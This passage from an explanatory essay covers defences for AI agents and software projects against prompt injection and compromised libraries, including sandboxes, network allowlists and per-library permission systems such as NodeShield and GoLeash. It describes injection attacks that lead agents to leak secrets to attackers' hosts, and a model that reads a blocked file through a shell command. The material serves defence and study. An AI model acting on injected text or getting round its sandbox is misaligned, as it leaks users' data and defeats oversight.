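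Independence between outcomes matters less for an attacker who sends one message to many companies. If the average chance of success is 1%, the expected number of victims among 10,000 companies is 100, whether or not the outcomes are related. But when all the companies use the same model, their failures are likely to be correlated, so most messages will fail everywhere and occasionally one will work on a large share of the targets.

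### Why most alarms can be false

A company also needs to know how often an alarm is right. Suppose one document in 10,000 is hostile, and a detector has 99% sensitivity, meaning it catches 99% of hostile documents. It also raises a false alarm on 1% of harmless ones. In a million documents:

| | Documents | Alarms |
|---|---|---|
| Hostile | 100 | 99 |
| Harmless | 999,900 | 9,999 |
| Total | 1,000,000 | 10,098 |

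Only 99 of the 10,098 alarms, about 1%, are correct. This result depends heavily on the assumption that one document in 10,000 is hostile. If one in 100 were hostile, half the alarms would be correct. The calculation also assumes that the detector works as well on new attacks as on those in its tests.

At these rates, if the invoice agent reads 200 emails a day, it would receive a hostile email about once every 50 days and raise about two false alarms a day. If the agent discards every email that triggers an alarm, some suppliers won't get paid. If the employee checks each one, they will look at about 100 harmless emails for every hostile one, and may stop reading carefully.

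People don't seem to be good at this kind of checking. In a study Anthropic published in August 2026, 1,053 paid testers worked with a coding agent that asked permission for its actions. The researchers replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it. Auto mode would have blocked 89% of these commands. This is a good argument for automatic screening over constant requests for approval, although 11% of the commands would still have run.

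A detector can be useful even if most of its alarms are false. The one in the table stops 99 of 100 hostile documents, but it may stop a smaller share of the attacks that matter most, the ones that would otherwise fool the model. Adding probes to Opus 5 reduced successful attempts by about two-thirds in coding and by just over half in computer use. For the related model Mythos 5, the rate of successful attempts in coding fell only from 0.45% to 0.41%.

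The same arithmetic applies to a package scanner. Almost all new releases are harmless, so even a low rate of false alarms can produce more warnings than a small team can investigate. Raising the threshold for a warning reduces their number but also lets more malicious packages through.

### Detection time and exposure time

A waiting period works only if somebody discovers a hostile release and the registry removes it before the period ends. npm removed the hostile axios releases within about three and a half hours, so a one-day delay would have kept them out. Even a one-month delay would not have kept out the hostile event-stream release, because the first alarm came 46 days after it was released.

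The scanner reportedly flagged plain-crypto-js at about 00:05, six minutes after the attackers published the hostile version. The publication times in Datadog Security Labs' timeline fit this account, but the timeline doesn't include the alarm, so it can't confirm when the alarm came.

Even if the report is right, the alarm alone protected few people. npm did not replace plain-crypto-js with a harmless placeholder until 03:25, more than three hours after the alarm. The first infection Huntress recorded also came after the alarm. A quick scan helps if the installer waits for the result and refuses a flagged package. Otherwise, the package can run before the warning reaches someone who can act on it.

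In all but one of the seven incidents compared earlier, event-stream, people noticed a problem within about a day. This suggests short delays could help, though the comparison includes only attacks that somebody found. Attackers who know about waiting periods also have a reason to keep their code unnoticed for longer.

Waiting to install a new release also helps only if someone else finds the problem in the meantime. A user discovered the eslint-scope attack because the malicious script caused an error on their machine. If every user had waited a day, that error would have appeared a day later. A delay shared by all users still gives scanners and researchers time to examine the release, but it removes the warnings that come from early victims.

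A team can exempt urgent security fixes from the delay, but an attacker with stolen publishing rights can label a malicious release as an urgent fix. The team therefore needs confirmation from a source the attacker doesn't control.

Email has no good equivalent of the waiting period for library updates. Thousands of people may install the same version of a library, so one of them can warn the rest. A hostile email may go to a single company, and holding it for a day won't lead anyone else to examine it.

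### Fewer successful attacks, same damage

Screening is worthwhile. Opus 5 resists attacks that worked on models released only months earlier, and a one-day delay would have kept out most of the hostile releases described so far. Attacks that succeed less often also take more effort, and failed attempts give defenders more chances to notice them. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* describes the model as nearly immune in Anthropic's own software, though it reports that OpenAI admitted in December that the problem may never be fully solved.

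The expected loss in a year is roughly

number of attempts × chance of success × loss per success.

Screening makes each attack less likely to succeed and may discourage some attempts. It doesn't reduce the loss from a successful attack, which depends on what the agent or library can reach. Suppose the invoice agent receives 1,000 hostile emails a year, each with a 0.2% chance of success. The company can expect two successful attacks a year. If better screening cuts the chance to 0.02%, it can expect one every five years, but that attack can still copy every SSH key and cloud token the employee has.

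Making attacks succeed less often may be enough when the losses are small and the company can reverse them. People accept spam filters that occasionally miss a message because one more advertisement does little harm. But a single stolen signing certificate or emptied bank account may do more harm than the company can recover from, so an average over many years describes the risk poorly.

Compromised updates are rare but can be serious. Tan and colleagues cite an analysis by the security company Mandiant that traced only 0.2% of initial intrusions directly to supply-chain compromise. Yet one such compromise, of the axios library, gave attackers a way into computers at unrelated companies.

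The Frontier Model Forum reaches a similar view, although its members have a commercial interest in trusting the models and classifiers they build. It describes training and classifiers as probabilistic controls, which lower an attacker's success rate, and recommends against relying on detection alone. It also accepts that strict limits can make an agent less useful, and suggests combining them with probabilistic controls. In its example, the same injection does little in an agent with narrow permissions but can leak data from one with broad access to files and stored credentials.

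For the invoice agent, narrow permissions would keep the SSH keys out of reach of an email that got past the classifier.

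## Limits on the whole process

The most direct way to keep the invoice agent from accessing the SSH keys is to restrict its whole process. The operating system, or the runtime that executes the program, blocks any request beyond a fixed set of permissions. The check doesn't depend on why the program made the request, so it applies equally to requests caused by an injected email, a compromised library or an ordinary bug.

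### Ways to confine a process

The easiest limit to set up is a separate user account. An administrator can create one for the agent, let it read the mail folder and write to the ledger, and keep it out of the employee's home directory. A separate account doesn't usually restrict network access, and the agent can still start most programs on the machine.

A container gives a group of processes their own view of the machine's files, processes and network connections. Files outside the container have no path inside it, so the agent can't open them. But the container shares the host's kernel, and a flaw in the kernel can let code escape. The administrator can also open a way out by sharing too much of the host with the container. In its documentation for the coding agent Claude Code, Anthropic warns that access to Docker's control socket, which programs use to send Docker commands, is effectively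 access to the host.

A virtual machine runs its own kernel on simulated hardware. Hostile code that takes over this kernel still has to get past the hypervisor, the program that simulates the hardware. Virtual machines generally use more memory than containers and take longer to start.

Linux can also restrict an ordinary process with filters. One filter, seccomp, checks system calls, the process's requests to the kernel. It can block all network connections, but it can't filter by file name because it reads only the numbers in a call, not the text they point to. Landlock works on files and directories, so it can allow access to the ledger and refuse everything else. Child processes inherit both filters, and a process can't remove them once they apply. *OpenAI Codex CLI Sandbox Implementation Analysis* (Willison, 2025) describes a version of OpenAI's coding agent that used Landlock for files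 and seccomp for the network. On macOS, a system called Seatbelt does both jobs.

A firewall can enforce a network allowlist by checking the numerical address of each connection, but this is awkward when a service changes its addresses or shares them with other services. A proxy, a program that relays connections, can check host names instead. In Claude Code's sandbox on Linux, shell commands can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox. By default, this proxy doesn't decrypt the traffic, so it relies on the host name the command gives. Hostile code can sometimes name a permitted host but reach a different one behind the same hosting service, a technique called domain fronting.

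Language runtimes can apply limits too. Deno, which runs JavaScript, refuses access to files, the network, environment variables and other programs unless the user grants it. The company could start the invoice agent like this:

```
deno run --no-prompt \
  --allow-read=/srv/invoices/mail \
  --allow-write=/srv/invoices/ledger.csv \
  --allow-net=accounting-host \
  --allow-env=ACCOUNTING_LOGIN \
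  agent.ts
```

Adding `--allow-run` would undo much of this, because Deno's checks don't apply to the programs it starts.

Node.js has a similar `--permission` flag, with exceptions for files, child processes and, since version 25, the network. The network exception initially allowed either every host or none. Node.js's developers compare the permission system to a seat belt. It protects trusted code from its own mistakes, but they don't promise that it will stop hostile code. It could stop the clean-up routine from deleting the wrong directory, but the company shouldn't rely on it against a compromised update.

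| Limit | What the check looks at | When | Trusted base |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate account | The account's rights to a file | When a process opens the file | Kernel, programs with administrator rights |
| Container | Whether the resource exists in the container's view | When a process looks it up | Host kernel, container software |
| Virtual machine | Requests to the simulated hardware | At each request | Hypervisor and the system it runs on |
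| seccomp | The type of system call | At each call | Kernel |
| Landlock, Seatbelt | The file and the kind of access | When a process opens the file | Kernel |
| Network allowlist | The destination's address or name | When a process connects | Kernel, firewall or proxy |
| Deno and Node.js flags | The file, host or program in the request | When the code makes the request | Runtime, kernel |

All of these limits can be static if their rules are set before the process starts. They also depend on correct settings, because misconfigured isolation can let through what it was meant to stop.

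### The invoice agent behind an allowlist

Suppose the company gives the agent its own account. The agent may read its program files and the mail folder, add lines to the ledger, and connect to the accounting host through a proxy, but it may not start other programs. An administrator owns these settings, so the agent can't edit them.

| Effect of an attack or a bug | With the allowlist |
|---|---|
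| Copying SSH keys and cloud tokens | Gone |
| Sending data to the attacker's own host | Gone |
| Running shell commands or starting a trojan | Gone |
| Deleting the employee's files | Gone |
| Reading other suppliers' emails in the folder | Remains |
| Adding false entries to the ledger | Remains |
| Using the login to send payment orders, including to the attacker's account | Remains |
| Crashing, or looping without end | Remains |

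The hostile invoice's request for a key now fails twice, first when the agent tries to open the file and again if it tries to contact the attacker's host. The remaining risk comes from the permissions the agent needs to do its job. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) makes the related point that a valid credential doesn't establish which actions somebody has authorised.

The company can also keep the login out of the process. Claude Code's sandbox can give commands a placeholder instead of the real credential, and the proxy inserts the real one only in requests to chosen hosts. If the invoice agent worked this way, a hostile HTTP library could still send payment orders while it ran, but it couldn't steal a login that would work from elsewhere. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to make the substitution, so it becomes a more sensitive part of the trusted base.

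These limits don't cover installation unless the company applies them there as well. For example, it could install the libraries in a container that can reach the npm registry but holds no credentials.

The table also assumes that the model runs on the same machine. If the company uses a hosted model, it has to add the provider's host to the allowlist, and an attacker can open an account with the same provider to receive the data. Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* collects several cases in which data could leave an agent through an allowed host. An allowlist is strongest when every host on it belongs to someone who won't pass the data on.

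### Allowlists compared with warnings to the model

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) compares how well an allowlist and instructions in the prompt stop leaks. The agent ran on a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, and had the simple task of summarising a web page that contained an instruction to send a secret from the model's context to the attacker's server. In 480 runs, the agent contacted that server 423 times. In 95% of the successful attacks, the summary gave the user no sign that anything was wrong.

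The researchers then tried several defences against one version of the attack, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs with an attempted leak | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Markers around the page's text | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and markers | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of hosts | 100% | 0% |

The 0% is not very surprising, because the test used an attacker's domain that was clearly not on the list, and a program that compares names will reject such a domain every time. The 100% beside it is more useful, since the attack fooled the model in every run and still got nothing out.

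The other percentages provide little evidence about current models, because the test put the secret directly in the context of a weak model with almost no other instructions. A newer model might follow the warning far more often. But a warning's effect depends on the model and the attack, while the allowlist treats a request to an unlisted host the same way regardless of either.

Lan and colleagues also had the agent send a secret in four pieces, which can defeat a filter that looks for complete keys. Splitting the secret doesn't help against a host allowlist, which ignores content. They acknowledge that a real attacker might go through a compromised site on the list, or through a trusted site that redirects visitors elsewhere. They didn't test leaks through DNS, the system that turns host names into addresses. A program that can look up any name can send out stolen data as part of the name,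 so the proxy should do the lookups, and only for permitted hosts.

A filter that blocked suspicious addresses also scored 0%, but this result deserves less weight. One of the filter's rules rejected any path containing the word "collect", and the paper's example attack sends its data to a path with that name.

### Permissions that are dangerous together

A developer who can't write such a short allowlist can still avoid certain combinations of permissions. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) gives that name to the three conditions behind the EchoLeak attack: private data, untrusted content and outside communication.

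A prompt injection can leak private data only if the agent reads the attacker's text, has access to the data, and can send it out. Removing any one of these conditions prevents the leak, even if the model follows every injected instruction it reads.

Willison thinks outside communication is usually the easiest of the three to restrict. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI released in June 2026, restricts it by limiting outgoing requests. Injected text can still reach the model and make its answers wrong. OpenAI's head of security said the mode was meant for people at higher risk and that it somewhat reduces functionality.

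Avoiding the trifecta rules out many tasks people want agents to do. An assistant that avoids it can't search the open web freely while it works on confidential files, or read a whole mailbox and reply to anyone who writes. Users can also create the trifecta by accident, by connecting several MCP servers that each seem safe. Willison points out that GitHub's MCP server had all three elements on its own, since it could read issues written by strangers, open private repositories, and publish proposed changes.

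The trifecta concerns stolen data, so it doesn't cover a fraudulent payment or a deleted file. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is broader. It allows an agent at most two of these properties in a session:

- It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change state or communicate externally.

If a task needs all three, Meta advises against letting the agent work without supervision, such as a person who approves its actions. The reasoning is the same as for the trifecta, but "change state" also covers payments and deletions. Meta illustrates the choices with an imaginary email assistant:

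| Property removed | How the assistant works | What the user loses |
|---|---|---|
| Untrustworthy inputs | It reads mail only from trusted senders | Help with mail from strangers |
| Sensitive data | It runs in a test environment without private data | Help with the real inbox |
| Unrestricted action | It writes only to trusted recipients, or a person checks each draft | Unattended replies to new contacts |

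The invoice agent has all three properties, because strangers send it email, it holds the login for the company's accounts, and it makes payments. Under the Rule of Two, it can't run unattended. Meta acknowledges that the rule is hard to apply to background tasks when asking a person for approval would be disruptive or ineffective.

Asking users to approve an action is also a weak substitute for removing the permission. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission requests. Most of those requests are probably harmless, but Meta itself mentions users who confirm warnings without reading them.

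The rule applies to a session, meaning one period of work with a fresh context, but memory poisoning can carry injected text into the next one. People can also misjudge what counts as "sensitive". An agent that browses the web and can overwrite research notes might seem to have no sensitive access, even though losing the notes would do harm.

Neither rule was designed for compromised libraries. A hostile library's code can run without an injected instruction, so keeping untrusted text away from the agent doesn't stop it. Removing access to private data or outside communication works against both kinds of attack, if the limit applies to the whole process and not just to the model's tools.

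### Finding out what an agent's tools can do

Developers can follow these rules only if they know what their agent's tools do, and a tool's description may not match its code. Santra, Kirat and colleagues (2026), in *ACaM*, cite research that found mismatches in 10% to 13% of cases among MCP tools. They also show how harmless-looking tools can leak data when used together. For example, one tool saves an API key in shared memory, another writes that memory to a log, and a third uploads the log to a debugging service.

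ACaM is a program that looks for such paths in an agent's source code before anyone runs it. It works in five stages:

1. It divides the code into the agent's control loop, its tools and their helper functions. It then finds the channels that carry data between them, such as files, shared variables and network calls, and gives each an initial label of public, internal or secret.
2. It lists the properties to look for, including patterns that involve several tools.
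3. It traces how data moves through each part, using static analysis, which examines code without running it.
4. It asks a language model about the few things the structure of the code can't settle, such as whether a condition is really a permission check.
5. It combines the results across all the parts, repeating this until no new facts appear.

The language model can raise a channel's label from internal to secret, but it can't lower the label or override anything the static analysis has established. These limits matter because a misleading description can fool the model that reviews a tool as easily as the model that uses it.

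Santra and colleagues applied ACaM to 43 real agents. On 24 they had labelled by hand, it scored 98.3% on a measure that penalises both missed capabilities and false ones. It scored 0.980 out of 1 at reconstructing attack paths the researchers had planted, against 0.903 for the best method using only a language model. In the unmodified agents, it found 123 paths to running code or exposing credentials, and the researchers confirmed all of them in the code. They built working attacks for ten of its findings. ACaM reported about 1,800 other paths, but only another AI agent checked those.

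The researchers assume that the attacker relies on a false description and doesn't write code to defeat the analysis. ACaM reads Python source code, so it can't examine a tool that runs on the publisher's server. When it can't determine what code does, it marks the code as unknown instead of safe. The scrambled install script in the axios attack might have been marked unknown if it had been written in Python.

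ACaM estimates what A(P) contains but doesn't block anything. A developer can compare the estimate with what the job requires and remove what the agent doesn't need.

### Default limits in coding agents

Coding agents are harder to confine than the invoice agent because they run unfamiliar commands and often need to download packages. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, as of June 2026, describes the defaults for Codex, and Cursor's *Run Modes* describes those for the Cursor agent. The table covers shell commands on the user's own machine. The Claude Code column shows the limits that apply after the user turns on the sandbox.

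| | Claude Code | Codex | Cursor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sandbox at first start | Off | On | On for commands that can work inside it |
| Files a command can read | Nearly the whole computer | A profile can block chosen files | The whole computer, except protected files |
| Files it can change | Project and temporary files | Project and temporary files | Project and temporary files |
| Network | No hosts until someone allows them | None | A built-in list of nearly 100 domains, plus the user's own |

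Claude Code's default protection is auto mode, a classifier that reviews actions before they run. Anthropic distinguishes permission modes, which determine whether Claude asks before acting, from the sandbox, which limits what an action can reach. A new user starts with a probabilistic control and has to turn on the sandbox, which the operating system enforces. Even with the sandbox on, a shell command can read SSH keys unless the user blocks those files, although it can't easily send them anywhere.

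Cursor's built-in allowlist makes it easier to install packages, but it includes GitHub and cloud storage services where anyone can open an account. Shai-Hulud 2.0 uploaded stolen credentials to GitHub, so the allowlist wouldn't have blocked those uploads. OpenAI takes a narrower approach when its own staff use Codex. It says its network policy allows expected destinations, blocks some others and requires approval for unfamiliar domains.

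The sandboxes in Claude Code and Cursor also leave some tools out. In Claude Code, the file tools, local MCP servers and hooks (commands that run automatically at set points) run outside the sandbox, so a compromised MCP server has the user's full access. Anthropic's remedy is to run the entire program inside a container, a virtual machine or its separate sandbox software. A model can also get around a limit on one tool by using another. Willison describes a test of Google's Antigravity in which the file tool blocked access to a file of secrets, and the model read it with a shell command instead.

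Exceptions can turn a fixed limit into a decision made during the run. If a command fails in Claude Code's sandbox, the model may request a retry outside the sandbox, and in auto mode the classifier approves or denies it. Cursor does much the same. Claude Code also runs commands without a sandbox if the sandbox can't start, unless the user has configured it to stop instead. An administrator can disable both the retry and this fallback, which keeps the limit fixed for the commands it covers.

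All three products protect some of their own settings files from sandboxed commands, which addresses Saltzer and Schroeder's problem of the user who can edit the rules.

Codex's cloud version separates installation from the agent's work. The setup phase can use the network to install libraries and can read any secrets the user has configured. OpenAI removes the secrets before the agent starts, and the agent works offline by default. This is a good defence against injected text, because the model never has the secrets and the network together. But an install script in a compromised library would run during setup, when both are available.

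Products don't start with the tightest limits partly because users would have to configure each new capability, which is why Anthropic calls sandboxing "safe but high-maintenance". But a confined agent needs fewer interruptions. Docker, for example, offers a sandbox that runs Cursor's agent without approval prompts and can keep the agent's login credentials on the host.

### One set of rights for every library and tool

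A limit on the whole process has to allow everything that any part of the process needs. If N(c) is the set of permissions that component c needs, the program works only if

A(P) ⊇ N(c₁) ∪ N(c₂) ∪ … ∪ N(cₙ).

Nothing separates the components inside the process, so each one still has A(c) = A(P). The allowlist makes A(P) much smaller, but the date library can still use the network because the payment code needs it. A hostile version of the library could search the process's memory for the login and send its own payment order.

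Every new feature also widens the permissions of the existing parts. If the company adds currency conversion, it has to put an exchange-rate service on the allowlist, and the date library can then contact that service too. A process-wide limit therefore works best for a small program with one job. A coding agent needs so many files and hosts that the allowlist may include a host where an attacker can receive data.

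Tool calls have the same problem. The operating system can allow connections to the accounting host, but it can't allow them only for invoices the employee meant to pay.

The company could split the agent into one process that reads email, with no login or network access, and another that makes payments. But the first process would still have to pass the payee to the other process, so it would keep some authority over payments without having permission to make them. Splitting the agent also takes work, because the two parts have to exchange messages instead of one calling the other directly. That work may be reasonable for two parts of an invoice agent, but hardly anyone would do it for 1,700 packages.

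## Permissions for each library

A program's parts can have different permissions without running as separate processes. A language runtime, or a monitor attached to the operating system, can identify which library is requesting a file or a connection and check the request against that library's list of permissions. In the notation used earlier, this makes G(c) small for each component c, while the components still call one another within one process.

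### Four permissions and a subset rule

Ferreira and colleagues noticed that many npm packages only do simple computations. A new version of such a package that suddenly wants the network is therefore suspicious. Their system gives each package a set of permissions, chosen from four:

| Permission | What a package with it can do |
|---|---|
| `network` | Import Node.js's modules for web requests and other connections |
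| `filesystem` | Import the module that reads, writes and deletes files |
| `process` | Import the module that starts and controls other programs |
| `all` | All of the above, and use language features that could get round the checks, such as `eval`, which runs a piece of text as code |

A module can import another module only if it has every permission the other module has.

Suppose the invoice agent's own code has the permissions {network, filesystem}, the HTTP library has {network}, and the date library has ∅, the empty set. The agent can import both libraries. If a hostile update of the date library tries to import Node.js's `http` module, which requires {network}, the runtime blocks the import because {network} is not a subset of ∅. The runtime also blocks the date library from importing the HTTP library to reach the network through it.

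To enforce the rule, the researchers changed how Node.js loads modules. Node.js gives every module a function called `require` for importing others, and the modified version compares permissions before importing anything. A hostile module might try to use another module's `require` through a property such as `module.parent`. The runtime therefore rewrites the code of modules that lack the `all` permission as it loads them, adding a check wherever the code might reach one of these properties.

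No npm package had declared its permissions, so the researchers used each package's code and dependencies to estimate which permissions it needed. They checked 30 estimates by hand and found that 23 were right. The other seven gave the package `all` unnecessarily.

The estimates covered 604,159 packages from February 2018. The researchers also looked at the top 100 packages by four measures of popularity or activity:

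| Packages | No permission | Some permissions | `all` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whole repository | 31.9% | 9.4% | 58.7% |
| Most downloaded | 27% | 13% | 60% |
| Most depended on | 15% | 15% | 70% |
| Most starred on GitHub | 14% | 1% | 85% |
| Most often updated | 33% | 11% | 56% |

A hostile update to one of the 31.9% of packages that need no permission can't import the file or network modules without openly requesting more permissions. The system doesn't limit a hostile update to a package that has `all`. Under the subset rule, 36.8% of the packages in the repository need `all` only because a dependency needs it. For example, if the date library imports a parser that needs `all`, the date library must have `all` too, and any hostile version of it will have the same access.

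The researchers replayed three real attacks, on eslint-scope, event-stream and electron-native-notify. In the last, the attacker published a useful package and waited for a cryptocurrency wallet to adopt it before adding the hostile code. Each hostile version received the same permissions as the version before it. None of those earlier versions had any permissions, and all three attacks failed.

The checks added an average of 0.2% to the running time of 20 command-line programs. Most runs lasted just over five seconds, so the delay was typically around ten milliseconds. The same delay would be a larger share of a very short run, but few users would notice it.

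### NodeShield

A hostile version of rate-map, a package that converts a number from one range to another, secretly loaded an unrelated package, dl-tar, and rewrote its code, apparently to break the installer for the PureScript programming language. *NodeShield* (Cornelissen and Balliu, 2025) presents a system that could have caught this attack either because rate-map had not declared dl-tar as a dependency or because it had never used files before.

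In the threat model, the attacker may control any number of packages in a Node.js server's dependency tree, including some that were hostile from the start. The trusted base includes Node.js, npm, its registry, and the program that lists the dependencies.

That list is a software bill of materials (SBOM), an inventory of every package in a program and the other packages each one uses. NodeShield lets a package import only the dependencies listed for it. A second list records which of seven capabilities each package needs:

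| Capability | What it covers |
|---|---|
| `network` | Connections to other machines |
| `file-system` | Files |
| `command` | Starting other programs |
| `system` | Environment variables and details of the machine |
| `crypto` | Encryption, which attackers use to hide code or lock files |
| `code` | Running text as code |
| `addon` | Loading native code, which a compiler has turned into machine instructions |

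If nobody has written the second list, NodeShield infers it by searching the source code for imports and for words such as `fetch` and `process`. The inferred list can grant too many permissions, because a word may appear in a harmless string, or too few, because some code builds the names of its imports while it runs.

NodeShield then makes a copy of the program in which each file runs in its own context, where the code can use only the imports and global names on its package's lists. If the code requests anything else, NodeShield logs the request, raises an error or ends the program, depending on its settings.

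This design avoids some of the excess permissions that the subset rule creates. Let E(c) be the capabilities that c's own code needs. While the program runs, c has only E(c), but a person reviewing the package sees

V(c) = E(c) ∪ V(d₁) ∪ … ∪ V(dₙ),

where d₁ to dₙ are the packages that c uses. If the date library uses a parser that reads files, the date library can't open a file itself. It may still get the parser to open one, which would make the parser a confused deputy. The reviewer therefore sees `file-system` beside the date library's name.

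Cornelissen and Balliu tested NodeShield on 67 hostile samples from 46 packages and found that it could have stopped 66. This total combines three kinds of test:

- Four packages had been harmless until a hostile update. NodeShield applied the capabilities of the previous version and stopped three of the attacks.
- Another 37 packages had no harmless version to use as a baseline. Capabilities inferred from hostile code may include everything the attack needs, so protection can depend on a developer who reads the list and refuses some of it.
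- Five packages ran hostile code in install scripts. The researchers started these scripts under NodeShield by hand, because npm normally runs them outside it.

The figure of 66 is therefore closer to a best case than to a prediction. The attack that NodeShield missed was on node-ipc, whose previous version already used files and the network, which was all the access the attackers needed.

In the event-stream attack, hiding the code would have worked against the attacker under NodeShield. NodeShield's search of flatmap-stream found only a need for `system`, because most of the code was unreadable. When the code decrypted itself and tried to use files, encryption and the network, NodeShield blocked it. If the attacker had left the code readable, the search would have listed those capabilities. A reviewer would then have had to ask why ps-tree, a package that lists a process's child processes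 and depends on event-stream, now needed encryption and the network.

The researchers also tried 29 known techniques for breaking out of JavaScript sandboxes. Only two worked, and both just altered shared objects, which NodeShield doesn't try to prevent.

NodeShield delayed responses from six test servers by less than a millisecond but increased their memory use by 43% to 251%. A few short command-line programs took about five times as long to run with it. Of 86 packages and applications, 83 worked with it. In a test of 24 harmless programs, NodeShield raised 18 false alarms and correctly allowed at least 387 uses of capabilities. The test ran only about 15% of the lines of code on average, so longer use might well produce more false alarms.

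### GoLeash

In Go, the compiler combines all of a program's packages into one file. When the program makes a system call, the kernel can't tell which package is responsible. Cesarano, Monperrus and Natella (2025), in *GoLeash*, recover this information from the call stack, the record of which function called which. Their system works in four steps:

1. A small program in the kernel records each system call and the call stack behind it.
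2. GoLeash reads the stack backwards from the most recent function. It skips Go's standard library and holds the first other package it finds responsible.
3. It translates the system call into one of 17 capabilities, such as reading a file or connecting to a remote host.
4. It checks whether the policy gives that package the capability, and whether the chain of packages leading to the call also appears in the policy.

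Checking the chain defends against confused deputies. If the invoice agent were a Go program, its policy might permit the chain "agent → HTTP library" to connect to a host. If a hostile date library called the HTTP library, the chain would be "agent → date library → HTTP library", and GoLeash would report a violation even though the HTTP library is allowed to connect.

Developers create the policy by running the program with its tests or a typical workload, recording what each package does, and reviewing the result. The threat model covers compromised updates to trusted packages, but not code that runs while developers build or test the program. Attackers may hide their code in C, assembly or a separate program. GoLeash trusts the kernel and the Go runtime, and assumes the attacker can't falsify the call stack. This assumption is strong because C or assembly code in the same process could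 in principle write to the stack's memory.

The researchers found no public collection of hostile Go packages, so they wrote five hostile behaviours modelled on attacks in other languages. They used five real programs, including Kubernetes, which manages containers across many machines. They inserted each behaviour separately into each of the 653 packages that the workloads had used, producing 3,265 hostile variants. For comparison, they combined each program's policy into a single list for the whole process. The table gives the range of detection rates across the five programs.

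| Hostile behaviour | Process-level rules | GoLeash |
|---|---|---|
| Running a hidden command for remote access | 100% | 100% |
| Sending out system settings | 0% | 97.6–100% |
| Stealing data from the user's applications | 100% in three programs, 0% in two | 100% |
| Loading a hostile shared library | 0% | 87.2–99.3% |
| Downloading hostile files | 0% | 95.7–100% |

GoLeash averages 98% across the five programs, and process-level rules average 32%. Counting every variant equally raises these averages to about 99% and 36%, because Kubernetes supplied two-thirds of the variants.

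This is good evidence that a list for each package can catch what one list for the process misses, but the size of the gap depends on the test. The process-level rules caught two of the behaviours because the inserted code also used the right to change resource limits, and the original programs didn't use that right. The rules also had no allowlist of hosts. An allowlist like the invoice agent's could have stopped the system settings from reaching the attacker's server.

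GoLeash misses attacks that use only capabilities the package already has. Half the packages in Kubernetes use three capabilities or fewer, which leaves an attacker few to exploit, but some packages need many more. Hiding the attack code in C also made it somewhat harder to detect. For code that sent out settings, the detection rate fell to 92% on average, and to 77% in frp, a program that relays network traffic.

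GoLeash raised no false alarms, but it was tested on the same workloads used to create its policies. In real use, it would also report legitimate actions that those workloads never triggered. Capslock, a Google tool that reads Go source code without running it, can help find such actions. It caught fewer of the inserted attacks than GoLeash did in packages that the workloads used, but it could also examine packages that they never reached.

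GoLeash increased the processor time per request by 1.3% to 5.1%. It also needs the names of functions in the compiled program. The standard releases of Kubernetes leave them out, so an operator would have to build Kubernetes with those names included.

GoLeash can detect a forbidden call and end the process, but the first such call may finish before the process stops because the kernel passes each event to a separate program for checking. That one call could be enough to delete a file.

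### Mir and LavaMoat

*Preventing Dynamic Library Compromise on Node.js via RWX-Based Privilege Reduction* (Vasilakis, Staicu and colleagues, 2021) presents Mir, a system for libraries that are flawed but not malicious. In the paper's example, a library turns text back into data by passing it to `eval`, so anyone who supplies the text can run code. Mir sets separate read, write, execute and import permissions for the things a library uses from outside itself, down to individual functions. Under Mir, the example library could still call `eval`, but the code `eval` ran could not load the file module.

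Mir stopped 61 of 63 attacks and added 1.93% to running time. Vasilakis and colleagues exclude libraries whose authors are hostile, so this result is weak evidence about compromised updates. It is relevant to bugs, though, because limiting a flawed library's permissions also protects against people who send it hostile input.

LavaMoat is an industry tool that puts packages in compartments and can also manage install scripts. According to Cornelissen and Balliu, it gives stronger guarantees than NodeShield, including protection for the objects that packages share. In return, it requires code to stay within a subset of JavaScript, which some existing packages don't do.

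### The date library and the HTTP library

Suppose attackers publish hostile updates to both of the invoice agent's libraries. The table compares the process-wide allowlist from the previous section with per-library permissions, under which the date library has none and the HTTP library has only `network`.

| Hostile action | Process allowlist | Library permissions | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| Date library sends a payment order to the accounting host | Possible | Blocked | Blocked |
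| HTTP library reads suppliers' emails from the folder | Possible | Blocked | Blocked |
| HTTP library sends the login to the attacker's host | Blocked | Possible | Blocked |
| HTTP library changes the payee in an order | Possible | Possible | Possible |
| Date library returns wrong due dates | Possible | Possible | Possible |

In all three systems, a network permission determines whether a library can connect but not where. An HTTP library that sends data to a new host has therefore stayed within its rights, just as the hostile version of node-ipc did. The allowlist has the opposite weakness, because it controls the destination but not which library connects. If S is what the allowlist permits and L(c) is what the library's own permissions allow, then using both gives

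G(c) = S ∩ L(c).

For the HTTP library, this is the right to contact the accounting host and nothing else.

Each library's permission could specify a host or folder. Ferreira and colleagues considered rights to a single folder but rejected them as more complex and slower to check. Cesarano and colleagues suggest checking destinations and file paths as future work.

Broad permissions are also a problem when there is no attacker. If the HTTP library keeps temporary files, it needs the `filesystem` permission, which in both Node.js systems covers every file the process can reach. The faulty clean-up routine described earlier could still delete the employee's home directory unless the process-wide allowlist stopped it.

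### Ways around library permissions

Native code and other programs can escape limits that a JavaScript runtime enforces. NodeShield can stop a package from loading native code or starting a program, but it can't control what either does once it is running. Granting `addon` or `command` is therefore close to granting everything. GoLeash can follow both because it watches system calls. But when a Go program starts another program, GoLeash uses a single permission list for the whole second program.

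A library can also use what other components pass to it. Suppose the agent passes its entire settings object to the date library so that the library can look up the preferred date format. If the object also contains a function that sends web requests, a hostile date library can call that function. Both NodeShield and Ferreira and colleagues' system permit this. In a Go version of the agent, GoLeash would probably report the call, because the date library would appear in the chain.

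JavaScript packages share some global objects, which can give an attacker another route. A hostile library could alter a built-in object and change how the payment code behaves when it next uses that object. Under Ferreira and colleagues' rules, a package needs `all` to change built-in objects. NodeShield lets packages change them because some harmless packages do so to add missing features. Under NodeShield, a package with no capabilities could therefore influence one with network access.

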